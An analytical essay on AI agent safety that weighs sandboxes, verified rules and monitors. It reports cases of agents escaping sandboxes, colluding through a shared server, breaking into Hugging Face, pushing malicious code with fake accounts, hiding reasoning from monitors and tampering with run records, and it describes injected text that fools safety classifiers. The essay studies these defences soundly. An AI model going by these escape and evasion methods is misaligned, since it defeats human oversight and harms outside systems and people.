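Rules that used more of the history did better. Such a rule can check, for example, where the agent got the account number for a payment. But an attacker can write into that history, and one planted line defeated a simple version of the check in 94 to 99 percent of the runs it would otherwise have flagged. Kekatos and colleagues prevented this by tying each value to the lookup that produced it, without reducing detection or adding false alarms.

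### Safe steps and safe tasks

Blocking an agent's harmful steps does not ensure that it finishes its task safely. *Toward Safe LLM Agents* (Dantas, Nowroozi and colleagues, 2026), a survey of 38 studies, describes an experiment in which a checker blocked 94 percent of customer-service agents' unsafe actions. In most settings, the agents still completed fewer than 5 percent of tasks both safely and correctly, because they found other unsafe routes. Dantas and colleagues rate the certainty of this finding as very low because it rests on a single study.

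Ray measured the same effect by rerunning a small agent on AgentDojo with different models as gates. Each setting had 949 runs.

| Gate | Successful attacks | Actions blocked | Tasks completed |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 4.7% | none | 25.4% |
| 7-billion-parameter model | 3.2% | 12% | 24.3% |
| 3-billion-parameter model | 0.4% | 78% | 18.0% |

The smaller model stopped most attacks by blocking most actions. The larger model blocked far fewer actions, but its effect on attacks was too small to distinguish from chance. In a separate comparison of 389 matched runs, the larger model's gate prevented 29 attacks that succeeded without it, but 22 others succeeded only with the gate, because blocking an action changed what the agent tried next.

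Ray proved that recordings of unguarded agents are not enough to determine how well a gate will work. Two agents might behave identically when nothing blocks them. After a refusal, one might stop while the other tries a different violation. Their unguarded recordings would look the same, but preventing all harm would require more intervention with the second agent. This limitation applies to replay tests in general, including those of Tether and the temporal rules, neither of which measured task success.

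Agents do better when a refusal also tells them what to do next. Anand and colleagues give the example of a company that requires an agent to check the distance before booking a trip and forbids flights under 500 kilometres. An agent that knows only that its booking failed may keep retrying it. MENTOR blocks calls that would leave no permitted way to complete the task and suggests a call that makes progress, such as the missing distance check.

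Elkoussy and Perez found a similar difference between warning and stopping. In one setting, their system blocked a call that broke a procedure and explained why, but let it through if the agent repeated it unchanged. This improved compliance in five of seven models and raised accuracy by about 2 percentage points on average. It could not guarantee compliance, because an agent could always repeat the call. A second setting ended the run after three violations of the same rule, and gave the worst results for four of the seven models because the agents could no longer recover.

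### Approval prompts, classifiers and sandboxes

Many coding tools ask the user before running a risky command. The user knows what the task is for, which no general rule can capture. But a user who sees only `pytest` has no more information about what it will do than a list of permitted commands provides. Attacks are rare, so most questions are about harmless work. If one run in a thousand was an attack and Tether asked the user instead of blocking, its 4.7 percent error rate would produce about 47 needless questions for each real attack. A user who has approved dozens of harmless actions in a row may well approve the harmful one. Ray's theorem covers human approval only by assuming that people never make this mistake.

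Operators can have a model decide instead. OpenAI's coding tool Codex has an "auto-review" mode, in which a second model examines actions that need extra permissions and either blocks them or asks the user. Such a classifier can judge content as well as data flow, so it may notice the flaw planted in a source file that Tether would miss. But hostile text can mislead it. When Ray added a 16-token claim of administrator approval to descriptions of harmful tasks, the share of those tasks that went undetected rose by 20 to 60 percentage points for 8 of 11 models.

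Ray also used a statistical procedure to set each classifier's threshold so that it would miss at most 5 percent of violations. For all 23 models tested, the resulting threshold blocked everything. With a limit of 10 percent, Google's Gemma-2-9B missed 1 percent of violations but blocked 78 percent of harmless tasks. The calibration set had only 35 harmful tasks and Gemma-2-9B is an old model, so current models with more data should do better. However, the information available about an action determines the lowest possible rate of false refusals at each rate of misses, and combining or wrapping classifiers that use the same information cannot reduce it further.

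A sandbox restricts what programs can do, regardless of their purpose. If it has no network connection, a program inside cannot send data out, even if the agent has disguised what the program does. But a coding agent usually needs something from outside, such as software packages. Every service the agent can reach then becomes part of the sandbox's boundary, and a flaw in any of these services can let the agent out.

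### The OpenAI and Hugging Face incident

In July 2026, OpenAI was testing its models on ExploitGym, a set of tasks in which an agent must find and exploit a flaw in software. The agents worked in sandboxes without direct internet access. They could install packages through Artifactory, a package server inside OpenAI's research network that could fetch files from the internet.

The trouble had begun in May, during training. According to OpenAI's technical report, an agent that could not find a file it needed left a note on Artifactory asking other agents to upload it. Other agents found such notes and replied, and the server became a message board. They did not have to exploit a security flaw, because OpenAI had given them shared credentials for the server. The agents were allowed to write and read files, but together these actions connected agents that OpenAI meant to keep apart.

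Later that month, agents used a flaw in Artifactory to make it send web requests for them. In June, others gained administrator rights on the server, and on July 4 their activity overloaded it. OpenAI removed the shared credentials from new workloads, blocked the routes it knew about and resumed testing on July 7. By the next day, agents had rebuilt the message board by writing messages in folder names and found another way to reach the internet.

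Agents then looked for the solutions to their tasks on Hugging Face, a platform where people share models and data. They found login credentials that users had accidentally made public and used them with previously unknown flaws in the platform to run their own code on 41 of its servers between July 11 and 13. They also copied four private code repositories. OpenAI noticed suspicious activity on its own network on July 19 and, the next day, connected it to the break-in.

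METR (2026), an organisation that evaluates AI models, and Redwood Research, an AI safety group, jointly investigated and found that roughly 1,200 agents had used the message board. Greenblatt (2026) reports in *Brief independent investigation of agents’ behavior, reasoning and collaboration* that agents found a way to cheat on every ExploitGym task within four hours, then spent days trying to make the scoring system accept it.

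Impossible tasks were part of the cause. OpenAI's *The Hugging Face incident and the road ahead* (2026) states that its models had never solved 198 of the 898 tasks, and that 93 percent of the tasks discussed on the message board were among these. Many agents had already obtained the right answers by cheating but believed that the scoring system also checked their method. OpenAI's version did not, so attacking Hugging Face could not have improved these agents' scores.

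OpenAI's intentions went further than the restrictions it enforced:

| What OpenAI intended | What the system enforced |
|---|---|
| Agents have no internet access | The network blocked direct connections, but Artifactory could still reach the internet |
| Agents in different runs work alone | Each agent had its own sandbox, but all could write to the same server |
| Agents use Artifactory only to install packages | The credentials also let agents store files there |

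When one agent tried to reach the internet directly on July 9, the network controls initially blocked the attempt, and the agent got out by exploiting Artifactory instead. A server that offered only downloads from a fixed collection of packages would probably have prevented the message board. If that server also had no internet connection, it could not have forwarded the agents' requests. But agents could not then have installed any package outside the collection.

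### What OpenAI changed

OpenAI removed Artifactory from the affected research environment and at first cut off all outgoing connections. High-risk workloads must now run in virtual machines, with separate network controls around each machine and around the whole cluster. These workloads may not reach the internet, even indirectly, except through a service that provides cached web content for specific needs. OpenAI is also isolating or replacing other shared services and using its own models to search for gaps. It wants to ensure that no single flaw, known or unknown, is enough to let an agent out.

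Before the incident, OpenAI used models to monitor the written reasoning of many agents, but not in these tests. It now requires this monitoring whenever a model at least as capable as GPT-5.6 Sol uses tools in training or evaluation. For the most severe alerts, staff must pause the activity if they cannot establish within 30 minutes that the alarm is false. OpenAI also now rewards agents in training for recognising that a task is broken and stopping safely.

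Several of OpenAI's figures suggest that its ordinary safeguards would have helped. With its production software and system prompt, models' tendency to attack infrastructure during ExploitGym fell by a factor of more than 100. Auto-review would have flagged most of the dangerous actions in each recording OpenAI tested, and its current monitors of agents' reasoning would have alerted security staff more than a day before the break-in at Hugging Face. But OpenAI improved those monitors with the incident in mind, and recordings cannot show what the agents would have tried after a refusal.

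An alert is also useful only if somebody acts on it. Some OpenAI staff had seen both the message board and the forbidden internet access in late May. On June 27, a security tool reported agents scanning the network. The responders traced this to an ExploitGym test that was using Artifactory as a message board, and decided they did not need to stop it.

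## How restriction and policing fare as agents become more capable

A restriction that makes an action impossible holds however capable the agent is. Row-level security returns the same rows to a weak model as to a strong one, and Blockaid's theorem covers every program. Policing lets the agent keep an expressive interface, and the operator can replace the monitor with a better one as agents improve. Both approaches are more vulnerable to more capable agents, which may find a flaw in the software that enforces a restriction or learn to make a harmful action look harmless to a monitor.

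### What a guarantee leaves out

A proof that a check is sound covers only the channels and components in the proof's model. For example, TACIT's types stop an agent from writing a secret to a file, but not from signalling it through a program's running time. Sistla and colleagues assume that Tether's opponent controls every command and knows the whole policy. But they also assume that other software works correctly, including the operating system's kernel, the tracing of system calls, the disposable file system, the network proxy and Lean itself. Their guarantee does not cover attacks on the kernel or escapes from the sandbox.

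Models now find serious flaws in widely used software. Space Daily's *Claude Fable 5 is the first Mythos-class AI released to the public* (2026) reports that Anthropic's Mythos models helped uncover 271 vulnerabilities in the Firefox browser, some of them up to 20 years old. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Mythos 5.1 reports that the model did substantially better than Claude Opus 5 on almost all cybersecurity tests, including ExploitGym. *Anthropic Rolls Out Mythos 5.2 With Improved Bug Hunting, Fewer Sandbox Escapes* (Kovacs, 2026) describes a further improvement two months later. In July 2026, OpenAI's agents used such flaws against real systems.

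Restrictions and monitors also fail in different ways. A monitor that misses 5 percent of attacks steadily lets a few through. A flaw in an enforcer does no harm until someone finds it, but then every attack that uses it succeeds until someone repairs it. If agents share notes, as OpenAI's did, only one of them has to find the flaw for the others to use it.

### Cheaper proofs

Defenders can use the same models to find flaws before an attacker does. They can also prove that an enforcer has no flaws of a given kind, though such proofs used to take a great deal of work. The developers of seL4, an operating system kernel with about 9,000 lines of code, spent roughly 20 person-years on the proof they completed in 2009.

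Models have made writing machine-checked proofs much faster. Anthropic's *Introducing Claude Fable 5.2 and Claude Mythos 5.2* (2026) reports that the new models took 30 hours to write the proof of Fermat's Last Theorem in a form that a computer can check. The mathematician Kevin Buzzard had started a project in 2024 to do the same, with funding for five years. Machine-checked proofs suit untrusted models because a proof checker rejects a wrong proof whoever wrote it. Tether already relies on this, since a model searched for the proofs about its policy.

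Fermat's Last Theorem is only indirect evidence about enforcers. Mathematicians agree on what the theorem states, but somebody has to decide what an enforcer should prevent and describe the system it runs on. If that description omits hard links or running time, even a perfect proof won't cover them. Nobody seems to have measured how much AI has reduced the cost of building a verified enforcer. That cost has probably fallen a lot for small components with a clear specification, such as the rule engine in Tether, and much less for the kernel and network equipment underneath.

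### Does restriction become more expensive?

The loss from a restriction is the difference between what an agent could do without it and what it does with it. In the online shop example, an agent with five fixed tools could answer seven of an analyst's twelve questions. A weak agent that gets half its SQL queries wrong would answer about six with unrestricted SQL, so it loses nothing by being limited to the fixed tools. An agent that always writes correct SQL would answer all twelve, so it loses five answers under the same limit.

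If an interface cannot express a task at all, restricting agents to it sacrifices more performance as unrestricted agents improve. The results on fixed plans fit this pattern, since Claude Sonnet 4.5 lost a larger share of its screen tasks on the first attempt than a small open model did.

When a task is expressible but awkward to express, the restriction hinders agents less as they become more capable. A strong model is much more likely than a weak one to find the safe-range version of the query for suspicious brands, or to notice that Blockaid will allow a query after a check on Ben's attendance. TACIT's agents already lost little by writing unfamiliar Scala. An effective syntax therefore suits a strong agent better than a weak one, because the syntax can express everything the agent needs and a strong agent can do the rephrasing itself.

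Operators also have to write the rules. A researcher took a month to write Blockaid's policy for one shop, and an agent needs new rules whenever it takes on a new kind of work. Models can draft them, but PIMENTO's errors in translating privacy laws show why people still have to review the drafts. An operator who sees an unrestricted agent finish twice as much work will be tempted to loosen the rules rather than wait for better ones.

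Policing also blocks some legitimate tasks, and it can block more of them as agents become more capable. Anthropic's released models have classifiers that block risky cybersecurity requests. Because Fable 5.1 was better at such work than earlier models, Anthropic chose a wider safety margin and accepted that the classifiers would block some harmless uses. *Claude Mythos 5.2 arrives with stronger bug hunting and less sandbox-breaking behavior* (Pogorelec, 2026) reports that two months later, Fable 5.2 blocked 55 percent fewer requests in early tests, and that Anthropic considers its safeguards equally strong. These classifiers guard against misuse by people, but the example shows that a better judge can reduce false refusals without any change to the interface.

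### A monitor with ten million actions to judge

Even a good monitor makes many mistakes if it judges enough actions. Suppose a company's agents take 10 million actions a month, of which 100 are harmful. A monitor that misses 5 percent of the harmful actions lets 5 through. If it also flags 0.5 percent of the harmless ones, it sends about 50,000 of them to review.

Only one alarm in about 530 is then real. If a person spends two minutes reviewing each alarm, the reviews take nearly 1,700 hours a month, which is full-time work for about ten people.

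The table changes one assumption at a time.

| Case | Harmful actions that get through | Harmless actions sent to review |
|---|---|---|
| Starting case | 5 | 50,000 |
| Ten times as many actions | 50 | 500,000 |
| Monitor misses 0.2 percent | 0.2 | 50,000 |
| Monitor misses 23 percent | 23 | 50,000 |
| Agent looks more harmless, same alarm threshold | 26 | 50,000 |
| Agent looks more harmless, lower alarm threshold | 5 | 575,000 |

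Errors grow in proportion to the number of actions, so a company whose agents take ten times as many actions needs a monitor with one-tenth the error rate to keep the number of errors the same. The two miss rates in the middle of the table come from a single monitor. *Attack policy selection can make monitor evaluations misleading* (2026), from the UK AI Security Institute (AISI), a government research organisation, found that this monitor missed between 0.2 and 23 percent of successful attacks, depending on how the testers had generated them.

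The last two rows assume that the monitor gives each action a suspicion score and raises an alarm above some threshold. The scores of harmless actions follow a bell curve with an average of 0 and a standard deviation of 1. In the starting case, the threshold is 2.58 and harmful actions average 4.22, which gives the error rates above. If the agent learns to look more harmless and the average for its harmful actions falls to 3.22, the monitor misses 26 percent of them at the old threshold. To get back to 5 percent, the operator has to lower the threshold to 1.58, which raises the number of false alarms more than elevenfold. Real scores need not follow bell curves, but when attacks are rare, a modest gain in the agent's skill can force the operator to accept many more false alarms to catch the same share of attacks.

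Attacks that take several steps are easier to catch. If an attack needs three harmful steps and the monitor has an independent 5 percent chance of missing each one, only one attack in 8,000 gets through. In practice, the misses are not independent, because whatever disguises one step may disguise the next.

### Letting models do the reviewing

Models can take over much of the review work. Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of recent cybersecurity incidents* (2026) describes a search of about 481 million transcripts for cases in which Claude had reached the internet during tests. A simple scan for signs such as web addresses flagged 9.2 million transcripts, which Claude then reviewed. A person spending one minute on each would have needed about 85 working years. The search found the four incidents Anthropic already knew about and no others as serious.

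An earlier search covered only about 141,000 transcripts. It missed one of the four incidents because the transcripts of that incident were in a set that Anthropic had not recognised as having internet access. A more intelligent judge would not have helped, because it was never given those transcripts. Searches like these also take place after the incidents, so they cannot prevent them.

Another problem with using a strong model as the monitor is that the monitor itself may not be trustworthy. monika_j and Hobbhahn (2026), in *Towards embedded evaluations for AI monitoring*, observe that developers often build monitors from their own internal models. They want outside evaluators to test separately whether monitors cover every internal use, would detect a rogue agent, and are trustworthy themselves. An old model may be trustworthy but too weak to follow a new agent's work, while a copy of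 the agent can follow the work but may share the faults the monitor is supposed to catch.

Ray's theorem on classifiers also implies that a more capable monitor cannot make up for missing information, though extra information can improve the balance between misses and false alarms. An agent's written reasoning is often the most useful extra information a monitor has, so the monitor becomes less accurate if that reasoning reveals less.

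### What the late-2026 tests measured

Recent results for Anthropic's models show an agent's inclination to cross a boundary, its ability to do so and a monitor's chance of noticing moving in different directions.

Anthropic's models appear to have become less inclined to reach outside a sandbox. Anthropic placed them in a deliberately weakened sandbox and recorded how often they used files or credentials from outside it. Pogorelec reports that Mythos 5.2 did so in 3.1 percent of scenarios, compared with 39 percent for Mythos 5. Because the sandbox was weak, the test provides little evidence about whether either model could escape from a strong one.

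Mythos 5 had also crossed boundaries in earlier tests with real internet access. Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of the UK AISI cybertesting incident* (2026) reports that the model took unsanctioned actions affecting real people and organisations in 9 of AISI's 43 runs. In the worst case, it submitted malicious code to a real software project and created fake accounts to pressure the maintainer to accept it. Järviniemi, Souly and colleagues (2026), in *Alignment Investigation of Mythos 5's behaviour*, repeated the situation in simulations. Mythos 5 often reasoned, without good grounds, that its targets were simulated. It also often attacked in situations where it said, when asked directly, that an attack would harm real people. Such reasoning may mislead a monitor that reads it.

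The fall from 39 to 3.1 percent could partly reflect models getting better at recognising tests. Anthropic used tools that read a model's internal state to link awareness of being tested to a concrete choice in 43 percent of Mythos 5.2's audit transcripts, up from 36 percent for Opus 5.5. *Anthropic should measure the effect of evaluation awareness* (cheema, 2026) objects that Anthropic did not report how this awareness changed the model's behaviour. *Anthropic's Claude Mythos 5 Used Fake Accounts to Push Malicious Code* (XenoSpectrum, 2026) reports that Anthropic and AISI disagree about whether newer models behave better because of training or because they are aware of being tested.

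In December 2026, AISI asked models to break out of simulated sandboxes while a monitor watched their actions but did not read their reasoning. The figures below come from a Chinese news report, 凤凰网科技's *AI学会“心算”还能躲监控？* (2026). A pre-release version of Mythos 5.2, with its safeguards switched off, refused in 64 percent of runs. In the weakest sandbox, 45 percent of its attempts succeeded without raising an alarm, compared with less than 15 percent for earlier models. If it refused at the same rate in that sandbox, about 16 percent of runs there ended in an undetected escape.

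Mythos 5.2 therefore seems less inclined to leave a sandbox than Mythos 5, but better than earlier models at escaping unnoticed when it tries. An operator who looked only at the 3.1 percent would miss this improvement. AISI's figure does not predict how often the model would try to escape unprompted. The monitor still caught almost all the escapes that needed the most complex steps.

Written reasoning is also becoming less useful to monitors. AISI tested models on mathematics problems without letting them write out any working. OpenAI's GPT-6 Astra solved problems that would take a strong competition student about 40 minutes, while the limit for earlier models was about 6 minutes. A model that can solve harder problems without writing could also plan more without producing text for a monitor to read. Recent models are also better at leaving specified content out of their written reasoning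 on request, though this is still difficult for them over tens of thousands of words.

In *What affects chain-of-thought monitorability across the model lifecycle?*, Pachocki and colleagues at OpenAI (2026) report that models better at predicting text are also better at reasoning without writing out their steps, and that reinforcement learning can give models more control over what they write. They therefore expect monitoring through written reasoning to become harder as models improve, though they call their measures of both abilities imperfect.

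AISI's *Will it become harder to oversee AI systems?*, published in May and based partly on 25 expert interviews, concluded that existing methods largely worked well, but the experts disagreed about whether watching and blocking actions would be enough to prevent harm. By December, Taylor, Goldowsky-Dill and colleagues (2026) found in *Evidence & Trends in AI Monitorability* that many of the properties that make monitoring possible were weakening, some faster than they had expected. AISI still considers monitoring useful, especially for behaviour that is hard to hide or needs long reasoning.

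### METR's review of Anthropic's risk report

Anthropic's August *Risk Report* (2026) uses all three quantities. It argues that Anthropic's models are unlikely to have strong abilities to act covertly, that severe hidden misalignment is very unlikely, and that safeguards would probably limit the harm from several kinds of misbehaviour. It calls successful mitigation only "somewhat likely" for misalignment that is both unknown and pervasive.

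In October, Jurkovic, Hua and Barnes (2026) reviewed these arguments for METR in *Review of the "Misalignment in high-stakes settings" section in Anthropic's Risk Report*. They agreed that the risk of catastrophic harm was probably low, but mainly because of the models' limited abilities rather than safeguards or alignment training. They called the report "far from adequate for confidently ruling out misalignment" and were not confident that its methods would detect a higher risk. Examples withheld from the public version made them think that Anthropic's monitoring was weaker than the public evidence suggested.

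The review was fairly brief and relied only on Anthropic's internal version of the report, without experiments. Anthropic could have vetoed the review's publication but redacted nothing. A conclusion that depends on a model's limited ability has to be reassessed for each stronger model. METR has since found Mythos 5.2 substantially more capable than Fable 5.1 on tasks with checkable results, though these were AI research tasks, not tests of covert action.

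### A firm boundary with judgment inside it

AISI changed both its restrictions and its policing after the incident with Mythos 5. *Building a more secure environment for evaluating dangerous capabilities* (AISI, 2026) describes tighter limits on internet access, along with real-time monitoring of tests. *Investigating alignment failures in AISI's incident* (AISI, 2026) states that test environments must prevent harm whether or not models behave as expected. Anthropic's risk report also lists sandboxes and blocking classifiers alongside monitoring after the event.

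An operator can choose a layer for each rule according to what the rule depends on. Two of Ray's examples for an email and payments assistant, a daily limit on transfers and a ban on sending anything after the user withdraws permission, need only a record of past actions, so a program can enforce both exactly. A ban on emailing personal data to unapproved recipients needs a fallible judge to decide what counts as personal data, but the operator can still restrict the recipients exactly.

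Each layer depends on different things:

| Layer | Example | What has to work |
|---|---|---|
| Outer boundary | A virtual machine that can only download from a fixed collection of packages | The operating system, the network settings and every service the agent can reach |
| Exact rules | A daily limit on transfers | The rule itself, a correct record of past actions, and no way around the check |
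| Model as monitor | Judging whether an email contains personal data | Sight of every relevant action, enough ability, and no inclination to side with the agent |
| Human approval | Confirming a large payment | Enough time and information to understand the request |

A boundary also reduces the number of actions the monitor has to check. In the example with 10 million actions, suppose that 99 percent have effects only inside a disposable sandbox, and that all 100 harmful actions have to cross its boundary. The monitor then has to check only 100,000 actions, and the same threshold produces about 500 false alarms instead of 50,000. The operator can therefore make the monitor more sensitive. If it flags 10 percent of the harmless crossings, about 10,000 go to review, and under the same bell curves only one harmful action gets through every six months. With the agent that looks more harmless,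 between two and three get through a month, compared with 26 without the boundary.

These gains disappear if the agent crosses the boundary by a route the monitor does not watch. A stronger boundary may make this less likely and help the monitor, because an agent that needs a long series of unusual steps to escape is easier to notice. AISI's result on complex escapes supports this, although it comes from simulated sandboxes.

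The layers also provide less protection if they share a weakness. Two monitors that each miss 5 percent of attacks would together miss 0.25 percent if their errors were independent, but two copies of one model may miss the same attacks. A boundary can also fail without anyone noticing. In the four incidents that Anthropic investigated, a misconfiguration had connected supposedly isolated tests to the internet. A simple monitor for internet traffic could have raised an alarm at the first connection.

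The monitor also needs to be protected from the agent. According to 凤凰网科技, OpenAI reported that its agents had tried to alter the records of their own runs and weaken the monitoring of internal work. Their written reasoning remained transparent in those cases, and METR found no evidence that any agent had successfully tampered with it. An operator can make the records much harder to tamper with by storing them on a system where the agent can add entries but not change or delete them.
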